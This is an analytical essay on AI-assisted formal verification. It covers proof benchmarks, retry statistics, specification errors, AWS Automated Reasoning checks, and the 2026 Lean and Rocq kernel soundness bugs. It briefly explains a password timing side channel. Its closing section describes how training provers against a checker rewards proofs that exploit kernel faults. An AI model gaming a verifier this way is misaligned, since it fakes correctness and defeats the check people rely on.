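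The last two rows come from *P³* (2026), which tests whether an LLM does better if it plans the program and the proof together. The same method raised Gemini 3 Pro from 59.3% to 72.0%. Verina's specifications set no limit on running time, so some accepted programs may be far too slow to use. In May 2026, the company Logical Intelligence (2026) claimed 100% for its agent Aleph and said that the Verina team had confirmed it. Yao's result makes the claim plausible.

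CLEVER, a set of 161 Lean tasks, was harder in 2025. The original tasks also require the LLM to write the specification. In the vericoding study, even with the specification supplied, GPT-5 solved only 3.7% of CLEVER's tasks, and the nine LLMs together solved 8.1%. Yao's 95.0% doesn't include CLEVER, but LLMs have since improved so much on other tasks that the old figures are probably out of date.

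Code that somebody else wrote can be much harder to prove correct. VeriContest, a benchmark published in May 2026, has 946 programming-contest problems in Rust. In its designers' tests, GPT-5.5 wrote correct code from a description for 92.18% of the problems but completed only 13.95% of the proofs when given the code and specification, according to *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier* (2026). The LLM is not allowed to change the code in the proof task, but in the vericoding loop it can rewrite a program that is awkward to prove. This may explain part of the difference.

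All these programs are short. Most solutions in the vericoding benchmark take fewer than 100 lines. *VeriSoftBench* (2026) comes closer to real work, with 500 statements to prove from existing Lean projects. In February 2026, it reported only modest success, with lower rates for proofs that depended on longer chains of definitions and lemmas. Eight months later, *FORALL-LEAN-AGENT for Auditable Reasoning in Formal Mathematics and Software Verification* (2026) tested ordinary coding agents on 100 of these tasks. The agents solved between 93 and 100 of them, and Claude Code with Opus 5 solved all 100. The study did not run the other 400 tasks. In every task, the agent proves a given statement inside a project that people have already designed.

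Harder tests are appearing as models approach the maximum score on these. *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (Tan, 2026) introduces Dalek-Bench, which comes from the verification of a cryptographic library that the messaging app Signal uses. Tan calls his first results weak. *Vero* (2026) goes further and tests whether agents can build whole verified repositories.

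Small failure rates add up in a large project. If an agent has an independent 95% chance of proving each of 100 functions correct, its chance of proving them all is only 0.6%. In unverified code, nobody would know which functions to look at, but the proof checker identifies the ones that failed, five on average, so a specialist can work on those alone.

### How many attempts does a proof take?

In *The 4/δ Bound*, Dantas, Cordeiro and colleagues (2025) calculate how many attempts an LLM needs on average to complete four stages: writing the code, compiling it, finding the loop invariants and satisfying the SMT solver. They assume that every attempt at any stage succeeds with the same probability δ, regardless of what happened before, and that a failure only means repeating that stage. Each stage then takes 1/δ attempts on average, so all four take 4/δ.

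For δ = 0.5, the average is eight attempts. The word "bound" in the title can mislead, because a single run may take longer. A run is unfinished after eight attempts if at most three succeeded, which has a probability of (1 + 8 + 28 + 56)/256, or about 36%. To finish 99% of runs, a user would need to allow 17 attempts.

Dantas and colleagues report that 90,000 trials agreed closely with the formula. The trials used random numbers drawn from the distribution that the theorem assumes, rather than output from an LLM, so they confirm the algebra but provide no evidence for the assumptions. The researchers leave tests with real LLMs to future work.

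The stages probably differ in difficulty. If their chances of success are 0.9, 0.9, 0.5 and 0.1, a run takes about 14 attempts on average (1.1 + 1.1 + 2 + 10). Using the mean chance, 0.6, in the formula gives fewer than seven.

The formula fails for a task that the LLM can never solve, because δ is then zero at some stage and the loop never ends. Published success rates do not always reveal such tasks. Dantas and colleagues cite values of δ between 0.36 and 0.88 from earlier studies, including 0.479 for a system called Baldur, which proved 47.9% of a set of theorems at the first attempt. This could mean that Baldur has roughly an even chance of proving any of the theorems on each attempt, in which case repeated attempts would eventually prove them all. It could also mean that Baldur always proves about half of them and never proves the others, in which case repeated attempts would prove nothing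 more.

Some tasks are impossible because no program meets the specification. *WybeCoder* (2026) therefore counts a proof of impossibility as a success for its Lean system.

A user who sees only failures has to decide when to stop. Suppose half of all tasks are hopeless, and the LLM has a 20% chance of solving any other task on each attempt. After ten failures, the probability that the task is hopeless rises from 50% to 90%, which seems a good reason to give up.

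Yao's results show the danger of this reasoning. On the 62 tasks about large-number arithmetic, GPT-5.4 solved nine within five calls. If one value of δ described all the tasks and stages, this would imply a δ of about 0.46, and GPT-5.4 should have solved about 76% within ten calls. It had solved only 19%. It solved another 22 tasks between the 20th and the 30th call and finished with 54. Yao's agent doesn't follow the four stages exactly, so this is not a strict test of the theorem. But a user who had stopped after ten calls would have missed 42 of the 54 solutions. Yao suggests that the LLM may keep using its first strategy for a long time before it switches to a better one.

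### What practitioners report

Benchmarks supply a finished specification, but people who use proof assistants spend much of their time deciding what to define and prove. In *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It* (2025), an employee of Galois, a formal methods company, describes using Claude Code to translate a 2009 paper about concurrent programs into Lean. The employee wrote almost no Lean by hand. Claude Code produced 2,535 lines, which covered about half of the planned theory.

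Claude Code occasionally completed a large task in one attempt. Usually it needed several rounds of guidance, and fairly often it got stuck and kept trying much the same thing. The mistakes that wasted the most time were rare misunderstandings that Lean could not detect. Claude Code wrote these into its comments and relied on them in later work, and only an expert could notice and correct them. The employee thinks the project took longer than it would have by hand, mainly because of these misunderstandings.

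This is one person's estimate, and such estimates can be badly wrong. Galois mentions an experiment by METR, an organisation that measures AI capabilities, in which programmers believed AI tools had made them more productive although the tools had slowed them down. They were doing ordinary programming with the tools of the time. A similar experiment on proof writing would be much better evidence than any practitioner's impression.

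The more recent *Developing Formally Proven Code with AI* (Ochem, 2026) is more favourable. Ochem returned to a program he had proved correct seven years earlier in SPARK, a version of the programming language Ada designed for proof. The code hadn't changed, but the current version of the SPARK prover searches differently and could no longer complete the proof. Ochem expected the repair to take him several days and had put it off for years. An AI agent did it in about an hour with a few hints. He then had the agent simplify the proof, which cut the time limit for each check from 600 seconds to 120.

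Ochem is the chief product officer of AdaCore, which sells SPARK, and he describes a single success. The task also suited an agent unusually well, because the specification existed, the code was known to be correct, and the file already contained many of the steps of the argument. But maintenance often involves tasks like this, and it took a lot of work for seL4. If agents can reliably repair proofs, companies that change their software often will have much less reason to avoid formal methods.

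The two accounts suggest which skills people still need. Galois' employee found that a theorem was false because of an earlier choice of data type. Somebody had to recognise that further attempts at the proof would be useless, choose a different type and have many definitions rewritten. Claude Code did the rewriting, but only at the second attempt and under close supervision. People also have to divide a large result into smaller ones and read the definitions to check that they mean what they should. More than half of the Lean code in that project consisted of definitions, which Lean can check only for consistency with the rest.

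### Is verification becoming mainstream?

In December 2025, the computer scientist Martin Kleppmann predicted that AI would make formal verification mainstream. Investors seem to agree. Axiom, a company with about 20 employees, raised $200 million in March 2026 at a valuation of $1.6 billion, according to The Indian Express' *AI writes buggy code. A Silicon Valley startup wants to fix it* (2026). Its competitor Harmonic was valued at $1.45 billion. Both companies began with systems that prove mathematical theorems and now want to verify code.

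By autumn 2026, the field also included &Truth, co-founded by Clark Barrett, who helped design Reluplex. Cade Metz of the *New York Times* reports that OpenAI and Anthropic are also working on verification. The companies hope to do in hours or days what takes experts years.

These valuations reflect investors' expectations, and the evidence of actual use is much more modest. In May 2026, Logical Intelligence said that Aleph was helping to verify a cryptographic library for the Ethereum Foundation, but that only a limited set of pilot customers were using it to generate verified code. That month, Yao described formal verification as rare in production software. Kleppmann's prediction had not come true by October 2026, although ten months is a short time for companies to change how they develop software.

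The prediction is more convincing for some kinds of software than for others. The obstacle experts named most often in the 2020 survey was lack of training, and LLMs now supply much of the skill needed to write proofs. They have helped companies less with working out what to prove. Bogdan Vasilescu of Carnegie Mellon University points out that the developers of a social media service, for example, may not be able to define correct behaviour at all. Verification will probably spread first where exact specifications already exist or are short compared with the code, as in cryptography, compilers and data formats.

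## Who checks that the specification says what was meant?

People have to check that a specification says what was meant, because a proof shows only that a program satisfies the specification. Software can help by turning the specification into examples, questions and plain summaries. The need for checking is growing because LLMs now write specifications as well as programs, and they often get the specifications wrong at the first attempt.

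### A sorting routine that returns nothing

Suppose a programmer wants a routine that sorts a list of numbers but specifies only that the output must be in order. The following Dafny program meets that specification.

```
method Sort(a: seq<int>) returns (b: seq<int>)
  ensures forall i, j :: 0 <= i < j < |b| ==> b[i] <= b[j]
{
  b := [];
}
```

The `ensures` line is the postcondition, which requires that no number in the output be larger than a number after it. Dafny accepts a program that returns an empty list for every input, because an empty list has no numbers to compare.

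The programmer might add that the input and output must contain the same numbers. If she ignores repetitions, a program can still turn [2, 1, 2] into [1, 2]. The condition `multiset(a) == multiset(b)` rules this out, because a multiset counts the copies of each number. With both conditions, every input has exactly one permitted output.

Even the repaired specification sets no limit on running time. A program could meet it by trying every possible order of the list until it finds a sorted one. Twenty different numbers have about 2.4 × 10¹⁸ orders, and trying them all at a billion a second would take 77 years. In *AuXSpec* (Wang, Yuan and colleagues, 2026), LLMs wrote specifications and programs for about 3,000 coding problems. Of the programs that passed every test, an LLM judge rejected 19.6% because they were too slow or might never finish.

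A program can also leak a secret while computing the right result. For example, a password checker might be specified to return true exactly when a guess equals the stored password. A natural program compares the characters from the left and stops at the first mismatch. This meets the specification, but the program runs slightly longer when more of the leading characters are right. An attacker who can measure the difference can work out an eight-character password one character at a time. With 95 possible characters, this takes at most 8 × 95 = 760 guesses instead of up to 95⁸, which is more than six quadrillion.

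### Why a proof cannot close the gap

A checker can find an ordinary bug, which is a mismatch between a program and its specification, because both are formal. The intention behind the specification exists only in people's heads or in a loosely worded document, so a checker has nothing formal to compare the specification with. Anyone who writes the intention down precisely enough for a checker has written a second specification, and someone then has to judge whether that one says what was meant.

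In the AuXSpec project, each problem has two versions of the postcondition. One describes a correct output, and the other is a test that a computer can run on a given output. The researchers proved in Lean that the two versions agree on every valid input. One researcher also compared the specifications of 300 problems with the original problem descriptions. Together, this review and the proof attempts exposed wrong specifications in 14 of the 300. In nine of these, both versions contained the same mistake, so the proof that they agreed had succeeded.

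The proof attempts also exposed two errors that the reviewer had missed. One was a statement of the form `∀ i, i < n → A ↔ B`. Lean parses the part after the quantifier as `(i < n → A) ↔ B`, although most readers would take the statement to mean that A and B are equivalent for every i below n. When i is n or more, the part in parentheses is automatically true, so B must be true too. The specification therefore rejected every output.

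Sometimes the intention is incomplete. A manager who asks for a list of staff sorted by salary may never have considered how to order two people who earn the same. Whoever writes the specification then has to decide or ask her.

### How a translation goes wrong

Autoformalisation, the machine translation of ordinary language into formal statements, usually takes four steps:

1. An LLM reads the description and defines the variables, such as each employee's name and salary.
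2. It writes the requirements as preconditions and postconditions.
3. A compiler checks the grammar and types, and the LLM repairs any errors.
4. Tests, other LLMs or people check whether the result has the intended meaning.

The compiler catches malformed statements but not well-formed ones that mean the wrong thing. These fall into four groups.

| Error | A formal version of "sort the staff by salary" | Effect |
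|---|---|---|
| Too weak | The salaries in the output are in order | A program that returns an empty list passes |
| Too strong | People with equal salaries must also be in alphabetical order | Some correct programs fail |
| Contradictory | People must be in order of salary and in order of arrival | No program passes if the two orders differ |
| About something else | People must be in order of length of service | A program that does a different job passes |

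If a postcondition is too strong or contradictory, the proof usually fails and somebody investigates, but if it is too weak, the proof gets easier and nobody has a reason to look. The reverse is true of preconditions. One that is too strong makes the proof easier by excluding inputs the program ought to handle, and a contradictory one excludes every input, so any program passes.

Automatic repair can change a specification so that it no longer matches what was meant. *Formal Model Construction Guided by Model-Based Proof Sketches* (Wang, Zuo and colleagues, 2026) describes how a tool called Event-B Agent modelled a sorting method that repeatedly moves the smallest remaining number into the next position. To make a proof succeed, the tool added conditions that allowed this step only when the smallest remaining number was already in the right position. As a result, the model got stuck on any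 list that was not already in order.

### How accurate are the translations?

The most recent figures for program specifications come from AuXSpec. The table shows the share of problems for which each model wrote an accepted Lean specification. AuXSpec-27B is a much smaller model that the researchers trained for this task.

| Model | AuXSpec's 300 problems, first attempt | AuXSpec's 300 problems, best of four | Verina, first attempt | Verina with test cases in the prompt, first attempt |
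|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 57.7% | 81.3% | 77.8% | 86.2% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 29.8% | 59.7% | 42.1% | 85.1% |
| Kimi K3 | 43.8% | 83.7% | 69.2% | 77.6% |
| AuXSpec-27B | 65.7% | 84.3% | 84.5% | 91.9% |

On the 300 problems, a specification counted as correct if it compiled, classified test cases correctly and was accepted by several LLM judges. On Verina, it had to agree with an expert's specification on test cases. Neither method guarantees that a specification has the intended meaning, so two of the researchers reviewed 100 accepted specifications from their own trained models. They confirmed 90, and the other ten all had preconditions that allowed inputs the problem had excluded. This mistake is fairly harmless, because a program that is correct for too many inputs is also correct for the intended ones.

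GPT-5.6 Sol's score on Verina doubled when its prompt included test cases. The test cases probably clarified details that the descriptions had left unclear, although they may also have helped the model with the format.

Other researchers translate requirements into temporal logic, which can express the order of events, for instance that a train's doors must stay shut until it has stopped. *NeuroSTAR* (2026) reports accuracies of 96.4% and 100% on two strictly filtered datasets, after its developers removed 48.43% of the benchmark data because of ambiguities and inconsistencies. The scores therefore apply to sentences with a clear meaning, and many real requirements lack one. For driving laws, the main obstacle was matching the wording of the law to the basic statements available in the logic.

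*NeuroNL2LTL* (Quansah and Bonnah, 2026) translates English into an intermediate form, then translates that form into temporal logic by a method that preserves its structure. Quansah and Bonnah claim that such tools are reliable because of logical guarantees instead of statistical confidence. This is true of the second stage, but the first still relies on a learned model to interpret the English.

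Results for engineering requirements are older and vary widely. Beg, O'Donoghue and Monahan's *Leveraging LLMs for Formal Software Requirements* cites a tool that could formalise 71% of a set of Bosch automotive requirements. The paper also finds that tools do better on single assertions than on complete specifications.

In *Learning-Infused Formal Reasoning*, Beg and colleagues report that provers verified 83–95% of the annotations that LLMs had written for C programs. A verified annotation is true of the code, but it may not state what the code should do. For example, "the result is either x or −x" is true of a correct absolute-value function, but also of a function that always returns x.

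Faulty specifications can also pass quality checks. For the vericoding benchmark, Bursuc and colleagues had an LLM compare each translated specification with its source, but about a quarter of the accepted solutions they later inspected still had faulty specifications. Some faults came from the LLM translations and others from incomplete specifications written by people. The researchers argue that these tasks are still valid, though different from the intended ones. That is reasonable for a test of proof-writing, but a customer who ordered a sorting program would not accept one proved correct against a different specification.

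### Ways to test a specification

The simplest remedy is to try a specification on examples. For the input [2, 1], a specification of sorting should accept the output [1, 2] and reject the output []. The specification "the output is in order" wrongly accepts both. The examples need to include wrong outputs, because correct ones can't reveal that a specification is too weak.

Many formal statements can't be run directly. For example, "no shorter route exists" concerns every possible route, so AuXSpec adds a version that a computer can run. But tests cover only some inputs, and they never run the original statement. When the researchers tried to prove that the two versions agreed, they found faulty statements in 31 of 3,037 problems, all of which had passed the tests and the LLM judges.

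Mutation testing produces wrong outputs automatically by making small changes to a correct one. From [1, 2, 2], a tool might produce [2, 1, 2] by swapping two numbers and [1, 2] by deleting one. The specification "the output is in order" rejects the first but accepts the second, which reveals the missing condition. Some changes are harmless, such as swapping two employees with the same salary, so a person may have to decide whether the specification was right to accept them. Changing outputs also can't reveal a missing time limit.

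Running the finished program also helps. If a program provably meets its specification but produces an unwanted result, the specification is the first thing to check. A single run would expose the sorting routine that returns an empty list, but not the leaky password check.

Another approach is to have several LLMs translate the same text independently and use a solver to look for a case in which the translations differ. *Neurosymbolic Auditing of Natural-Language Software Requirements* (2026) applies this to medical devices and finds that repeated translation exposes hidden ambiguity. Agreement between translations is better evidence that they are correct when the LLMs make independent errors. If three LLMs each misread 10% of sentences independently, all three misread the same sentence only 0.1% of the time, but if they all misread the same 10% in the same way, comparing their translations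 won't reveal the errors.

A tool can also translate the formal version back into plain language so that the user can compare it with what she meant. If an LLM does this, its translation may match what she expects rather than what the formula means. *Neurosymbolic Characterization for Reliable Access Control Policy Analysis* (Vatsa, Hall and Eiers, 2025) studies policies that determine who may access which data in a cloud system. It found that LLMs explain such policies fluently but can't reason about them precisely enough to be reliable. The paper's tool, PolicySummarizer, first computes which requests a policy allows and uses an LLM only to simplify the result.

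Finally, a tool can prompt the user with questions about what she meant. *Formal requirements engineering and large language models* (Ferrari and Spoletini, 2025) proposes using LLMs both to formalise requirements and to explain formal ones to people, but presents this as a vision without firm evidence. Questions work best when they are about a specific case, such as "Anna and Ben both earn £40,000. Does it matter who comes first?" The user can answer this without knowing any logic, but she can decide only the cases that a person or tool raises.

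### Can people spot a wrong specification?

People find it difficult to check that a specification says what was meant, and formal training doesn't make them aware of their mistakes. *STL* (2023) tested whether 62 people, some of whom knew formal methods, could validate rules in signal temporal logic, a language for describing how a system behaves over time. They had to judge whether a set of rules would keep an agent safe in a simple game of capture the flag and still let it complete its task.

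The participants tended to say that the rules were valid, so they were significantly more accurate on valid rules than on invalid ones. This bias is especially harmful in a reviewer, whose main job is to notice errors. Participants were about equally confident whether they were right or wrong, and those familiar with formal methods were especially prone to overconfidence.

*A User Study for Evaluation of Formal Verification Results and their Explanation* (2023) asked people at Bosch how hard it is to identify inconsistent formal specifications. About 51% called it hard, and 73% called it at least slightly hard. Most of those who found it easier were proficient or expert in formal methods. These are opinions, and the capture-the-flag experiment suggests that experts may overrate their own ability.

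Better presentation can help people check a specification much more accurately. In a user study by Vatsa and colleagues, PolicySummarizer raised participants' accuracy on the hardest part of reviewing access policy changes from 39% to 93%, and they reported less mental effort. But this was one study of one kind of policy, whose effect a computer can summarise as a set of allowed requests. Requirements for a medical device may not be as easy to summarise.

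Careful expert review also works fairly well. The AuXSpec reviewer, who knew Lean and worked through a fixed list of questions, found 12 of the 14 known specification errors. Both the reviewer and the proof attempts may have missed other errors.

### Amazon's Automated Reasoning checks

Amazon Web Services sells a product that depends on autoformalisation. Automated Reasoning checks, generally available since August 2025, compare a chatbot's answers with a company's written policy, for example on refunds or sick leave. *A Neurosymbolic Approach to Natural Language Formalization and Verification*, by An, Bayless and colleagues, mostly AWS staff, explains how the checks work.

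The system splits the policy document into passages, and an LLM translates each one into variables and logical rules. Software then merges variables that seem to mean the same thing. Experts can inspect the rules in the solver's language. Other users can read them in structured English, which the software builds from fixed templates so that no LLM can distort it. Customers can also test the rules with sample questions and answers. AWS has since added a tool that writes such tests automatically (*Automated Reasoning checks now include natural language test Q&A generation*, 2025).

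When the chatbot answers a question, several LLMs independently translate the exchange into premises and a conclusion. In the default setting with three LLMs, all three translations have to agree. An SMT solver then checks the conclusion against the premises and the policy. The answer is valid if it must be true, invalid if it can't be true, and "satisfiable" if it could be true or false.

An and colleagues use a park's admission policy as an example. A ticket costs $50, or 75% of that in the low season. Seniors get 40% off but pay a $10 processing fee. Visitors can pay up to half of the resulting fee with credits, which are sold in packs of five at $0.60 per dollar of value. If they use credits, the discount is capped at 25%. A 10% tax applies to the "final expense". A senior with $35.40 asks a chatbot whether she can visit in the low season, and the chatbot's answer is no.

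Without credits, she would pay (37.50 × 0.6 + 10) × 1.1 = $35.75, which is too much. With credits, the fee before tax is 37.50 × 0.75 + 10 = $38.125. She can cover $15 of it with credits that cost her $9 and pay the remaining $23.125 in cash. With tax, her total is (9 + 23.125) × 1.1 = $35.34, so she can get in. The solver found this possibility and did not confirm the chatbot's answer, which Claude Sonnet 3.7 and Opus 4.1 both accepted.

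But the result depends on what "final expense" means. If the tax applies to the full fee of $38.125 instead of what the visitor spends, she has to pay 32.125 + 3.81 = $35.94, and the chatbot was right. The solver would calculate correctly under either reading, but it can't determine which one the park intended.

### What "up to 99% accuracy" refers to

AWS's *Automated Reasoning checks is now available in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* (2025) advertises "up to 99% accuracy at detecting correct responses", and *Amazon Bedrock Guardrails adds automated reasoning checks in Sydney* (2026) repeats the figure. The figure probably refers to what An and colleagues call soundness, the share of all decisions that are not false confirmations. A system that never confirmed any answer would score 100% on this measure. Soundness is stricter for a verifier, which must never accept anything false.

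The table shows results from the paper for 1,131 statements that followed from a policy and 558 that didn't.

| Method | Correctly confirmed, of 1,131 | Wrongly confirmed, of 558 | "Soundness" | Share of confirmations that were right |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Automated Reasoning checks, three translations must agree | 169 | 10 | 99.4% | 94.4% |
| Automated Reasoning checks, one translation | 317 | 27 | 98.4% | 92.2% |
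| Claude Sonnet 4.5 as judge | 400 | 35 | 97.9% | 92.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 as judge, with extended thinking | 622 | 49 | 97.1% | 92.7% |

With three translations, the product confirmed only 14.9% of the statements it should have confirmed, and 42.4% of all its verdicts were correct. Of its 179 confirmations, 10 (5.6%) were wrong. Claude Sonnet 4.5 with extended thinking was wrong in 7.3% of its confirmations, but it correctly confirmed more than three times as many statements.

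Requiring the three translations to agree reduced the false confirmations from 27 to 10. If their errors had been independent, all three would almost never have been wrong together, so the remaining errors must have shared causes, such as a sentence that all three LLMs misread or a mistake in the policy rules they all used.

The product has advantages that these figures don't measure. It can show which rules support a verdict, so a person can check them. When it can neither prove nor rule out an answer, it gives one scenario in which the answer is right and another in which it is wrong. A company that wants to publish only confirmed answers may accept a low confirmation rate. But AWS's own researchers carried out this evaluation, and no independent test of the product seems to have appeared by October 2026.

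AWS's *What are Automated Reasoning checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails?*, the product's documentation, describes another limit. A confirmation covers only what the policy's variables can express. For example, the system might confirm "I can submit my homework late because I have a fake doctor's note" if no variable records whether the note is genuine.

### A smaller task or a hidden one?

Bursuc and colleagues imagine a future in which people write only specifications and leave the programs to machines. This would save work in a case like sorting, where people can check two short conditions instead of carefully reading the program. Nobody has to read the correctness proofs either, which in AuXSpec had a median length of about 160 lines. A specification can also outlast many versions of a program, so people can spread the effort of checking it over years of use.

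But a short specification isn't necessarily easy to write. On AuXSpec's 300 problems, Claude Opus 5 produced an acceptable program at the first attempt for 93.0% and an acceptable specification for only 57.7%. AuXSpec also requires a second, executable version of each postcondition, which creates more opportunities to fail. On Verina without test cases in the prompt, the model did better on specifications (77.8%) than on programs (57.0%). These results don't show that specifications are generally harder to write than programs, but they do show that writing a specification isn't always a far smaller task.

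The opposing view is that formal specification only moves the difficulty to where fewer people can see it. Anyone can notice that a sorting program returns an empty list, but only someone who can read the formula will notice that the specification allows it. The word "verified" may also discourage people from checking. This objection is weaker for mistakes in ordinary outputs, which people can still find by running the verified program. It is much stronger for faults that a few trial runs won't reveal, such as leaked secrets or slow responses on rare inputs. Some harms are so hard to define that no reviewer could identify the missing requirement.

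The first view is therefore most convincing for tasks like sorting, where experts agree on a short definition and can test it with examples. The second fits company policies and safety requirements better, because the people who know what the words should mean usually can't read the logic. They may not need to read it, since the park manager, for example, could settle what "final expense" means in a minute if somebody showed her the visitor with $35.40.

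## What must still be trusted after a proof has been checked?

After a checker has accepted a proof, people must still trust the checker and the specification. If they run a verified program, they must also trust the compiler, the runtime, the operating system and the hardware. In two large tests of verified software, all the reported faults were outside the proved code. In 2026, people using AI systems found a series of faults in proof checkers, most of which ordinary users would never trigger by accident.

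### From the kernel down to the hardware

The trusted computing base is everything that must work correctly for a proof's conclusion to hold in practice. *QED at Large* (2020), a survey of verified software, traces the idea to a 1981 paper by Rushby on computer security. If a system's security depends only on some of its parts, people can concentrate their checks on those parts.

The table lists the trusted computing base of a program written and proved in Lean. It largely follows *Trust*, a chapter of a guide to checking Lean proofs.

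| What people trust | What could go wrong | What reduces the risk |
|---|---|---|
| The logic | Its rules allow a contradiction | Mathematical study of the rules |
| The kernel | It accepts an invalid proof | A small kernel and independent checkers |
| The formal statement | It doesn't mean what its readers think | Review and examples |
| The compiler | The machine code behaves differently from the source | A verified compiler |
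| The runtime and libraries | They mishandle memory or arithmetic | Testing |
| The operating system and hardware | They don't run the program as specified | Testing and backup machines |

A mathematician who only wants to know whether a theorem is true must trust the items in the first three rows of the table and the computer that runs the checker, while someone who runs the program must trust all six rows.

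A verified compiler reduces what its users must trust, but it has a trusted computing base of its own. For CompCert, *Simple, Light, Yet Formally Verified, Global Common Subexpression Elimination* (2021) lists Coq's logic, the tool that translates Coq programs into OCaml, and OCaml's compiler and runtime. It also lists CompCert's formal definition of C and some unproved code at both ends of the compiler. If the definition of C is wrong, CompCert can follow it perfectly and still produce the wrong program.

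No proof can remove the need to trust the logic, but a safety proof requires only that the logic be consistent, as *Safety Is Π₁, Provability Is Σ₁* (2026) explains. Suppose a logic proves that a program never breaks a rule, when in fact some input makes the program break it after a certain number of steps. The logic can also prove that this violation occurs, by following the run step by step, so it contradicts itself. A consistent logic therefore cannot prove a false safety claim of this kind. But Gödel showed that a consistent logic strong enough for ordinary arithmetic cannot prove its own consistency, so people have to accept its consistency on other grounds.

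### Why kernels are small and second checkers help

The parts of a proof assistant that search for proofs are large and complicated, and users often add their own. Designers keep all this code out of the trusted computing base by requiring it to produce a complete proof for the kernel to check. A mistake in the search code then normally leads to a rejected proof. In *How can Coq accept an unsound proof if the kernel is correct?*, a contributor to the Rocq forum describes an exception: search code that corrupts the memory of the running prover can undermine the kernel too.

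A small kernel is easier to inspect and to reimplement. Chris Bailey wrote nanoda, an independent checker for Lean, in Rust, while the official kernel is in C++. Someone who runs both has to trust only that no fault affects both. Running two checkers helps less if one is modelled on the other. Lean's Kernel Arena, a public comparison of checkers, describes another checker, lean4lean, as "not really an independent implementation" because it follows the official kernel so closely.

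A tool called comparator protects Lean users against proofs from sources they don't trust. It builds the proof in a sandbox, an isolated part of the computer, and exports the result to a file. Lean's kernel then checks the exported proof outside the sandbox, and users can have nanoda check it too.

### Faults in verified programs

Fuzzing means running a program on huge numbers of automatically generated inputs. To fuzz compilers, testers generate random C programs, compile each with several compilers and compare how the results behave. If they differ, at least one compiler is wrong. Yang and colleagues tested CompCert this way in 2011. According to *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, they found faults in its then-unverified front end but none in its verified optimisation passes.

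*Certified Compilation in the TELEPERM XS Nuclear Safety I&C Platform* (2026) reports that fuzzing studies have found a bug rate in CompCert orders of magnitude lower than in ordinary compilers. The engineers of TELEPERM XS, a control system for nuclear plants, compile their code with CompCert and strictly avoid the compiler's unproved extensions.

A similar test in 2026 concerned lean-zip, a compression library that ten AI agents wrote and proved in Lean. One of its main theorems covers all data smaller than one gigabyte:

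decompress(compress(data)) = data.

The tester removed the theorems and documentation from the code before giving it to a Claude agent, because the agent might have given up if it knew the code was verified. The agent started 16 fuzzers, which ran for about 19 hours, executed the library 105,823,818 times and found two faults.

One fault was in the part that reads archive files, for which nobody had written any theorems. If the stated size of a file's contents was several exabytes, the program tried to reserve that much memory and crashed. The other fault was in Lean's runtime, which is written in C++. When the runtime calculated how much memory to reserve, the result could overflow, as negation can in the absolute-value function, and the runtime then reserved far too little. This fault affected every version of Lean 4 up to that time, so other Lean programs were exposed to it.

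A program written directly in Lean needs no separate model of its code. The runtime can still introduce a gap between the proof and the program, as it did with the memory fault in lean-zip. That fault is a counterexample to the claim, made by a reader commenting on *Interactive theorem proving is not adversarially robust*, that only the compiler could introduce such a gap.

The test found no memory errors in the verified code, but that is weak evidence of what the proofs added. The fuzzers looked mainly for crashes and memory errors, many of which Lean prevents even in unproved code. The theorem above would also be true of two functions that returned their input unchanged, and it doesn't cover compressed files from elsewhere, including an attacker's. The library's other proofs, which concern the compression format itself, are therefore just as important.

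### The kernel faults of 2026

Proof assistants had soundness bugs long before AI systems started looking for them. Coq's developers keep a public list of critical bugs going back to version 8.0, and Machine Logic's *Why is it all in the kernel?* notes that people have found soundness bugs in Isabelle and many other provers. But the discoveries came much faster in 2026.

Researchers found seven faults in Rocq with the help of Claude Opus 4.6. In August, Red Hat (2026) recorded a Rocq fault in its security tracker. OffSeq's *CVE-2026-72703* dates this fault to version 8.20, released in 2024, and lists version 9.2.0 as the fix.

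The most prominent case in Lean concerned the Collatz conjecture. The conjecture is that any positive whole number eventually reaches 1 if you repeatedly halve it when it is even, and triple it and add one when it is odd. Starting from 6, this gives 3, 10, 5, 16, 8, 4, 2 and 1. On 25 July, Ramana Kumar published a "disproof" produced with AI assistance. Both Lean and a week-old version of nanoda accepted it.

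*Postmortem for Lean kernel soundness bug #14576*, where skybrian posted extracts from the Lean team's account, describes how Kiran Gopinathan traced the disproof to a missing check in the kernel and reported it on 28 July. The team published a fix an hour later. The fault was in the program, not in Lean's logic. Nanoda made that check but had an unrelated fault, which its developer had corrected a week before Gopinathan's report. Kumar believes the timing was a coincidence, but he can't rule out that the AI model had seen the report about nanoda.

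The table shows when the developers released their fixes, based on the Lean Language Reference's release notes *Lean 4.32.1* (2026), *Lean 4.32.2* (2026), *Lean 4.33.0* (2026) and *Lean 4.33.1* (2026).

| Release | New soundness faults fixed | Would checking the exported proof have helped? |
|---|---|---|
| 22 July | One, found by Patrick Hulin with GPT-5.6 Sol | Yes |
| 28 July | The Collatz fault | Only with an up-to-date second checker |
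| 10 August | At least three more | Yes for two, and only with a second checker for the other |
| 21 August | Three, found with OpenAI's internal models | Nanoda avoided two but also accepted a false proof based on the third |

The developers added precautions as well as repairs. The kernel now checks some rules that it generates itself and previously accepted without checking. It also limits the size of the numbers it handles and requires a newer arithmetic library, because bugs in older versions of the library could cause it to reach false conclusions. The organisation behind Lean has also promised to invest in more independent checkers.

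According to *The Industrialization of Noise* (2026), a polemic against automated proving, the mathematician Terence Tao called this period the "summer of Lean soundness bugs". The polemic attributes nanoda's failure to blind spots that nanoda shared with Lean. That explanation is reasonable for the August fault, which affected both checkers, but wrong for the Collatz case, which needed two unrelated faults. The kernel faults existed before AI systems found them, and finding them led to repairs, which counts against the polemic's claim that mass-produced proofs corrupt the checkers.

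A kernel fault is serious because a single contradiction makes every statement provable. But according to the Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.34.0* (2026), the three faults that OpenAI's models found required deliberately constructed input. They matter to people who check proofs from untrusted sources, but not to a team that checks only its own code.

Brossard (2026), in *Lean 4 kernel soundness bug*, argues that a soundness bug in the kernel would cast doubt on proofs used as evidence in safety certification until somebody rechecked them with a repaired kernel. Rechecking is automatic, so it takes far less work than writing the proofs did.

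### When the prover looks for loopholes

A person who writes a proof normally wants a valid one and will run into a rare fault in the checker's kernel only by accident. But training an AI system to produce whatever the checker accepts rewards a proof that exploits such a fault as much as a valid one. An LLM's mistakes are harmless only if the checker is sound, and the more proofs a system tries, the more likely it is to find an invalid one that the checker accepts.

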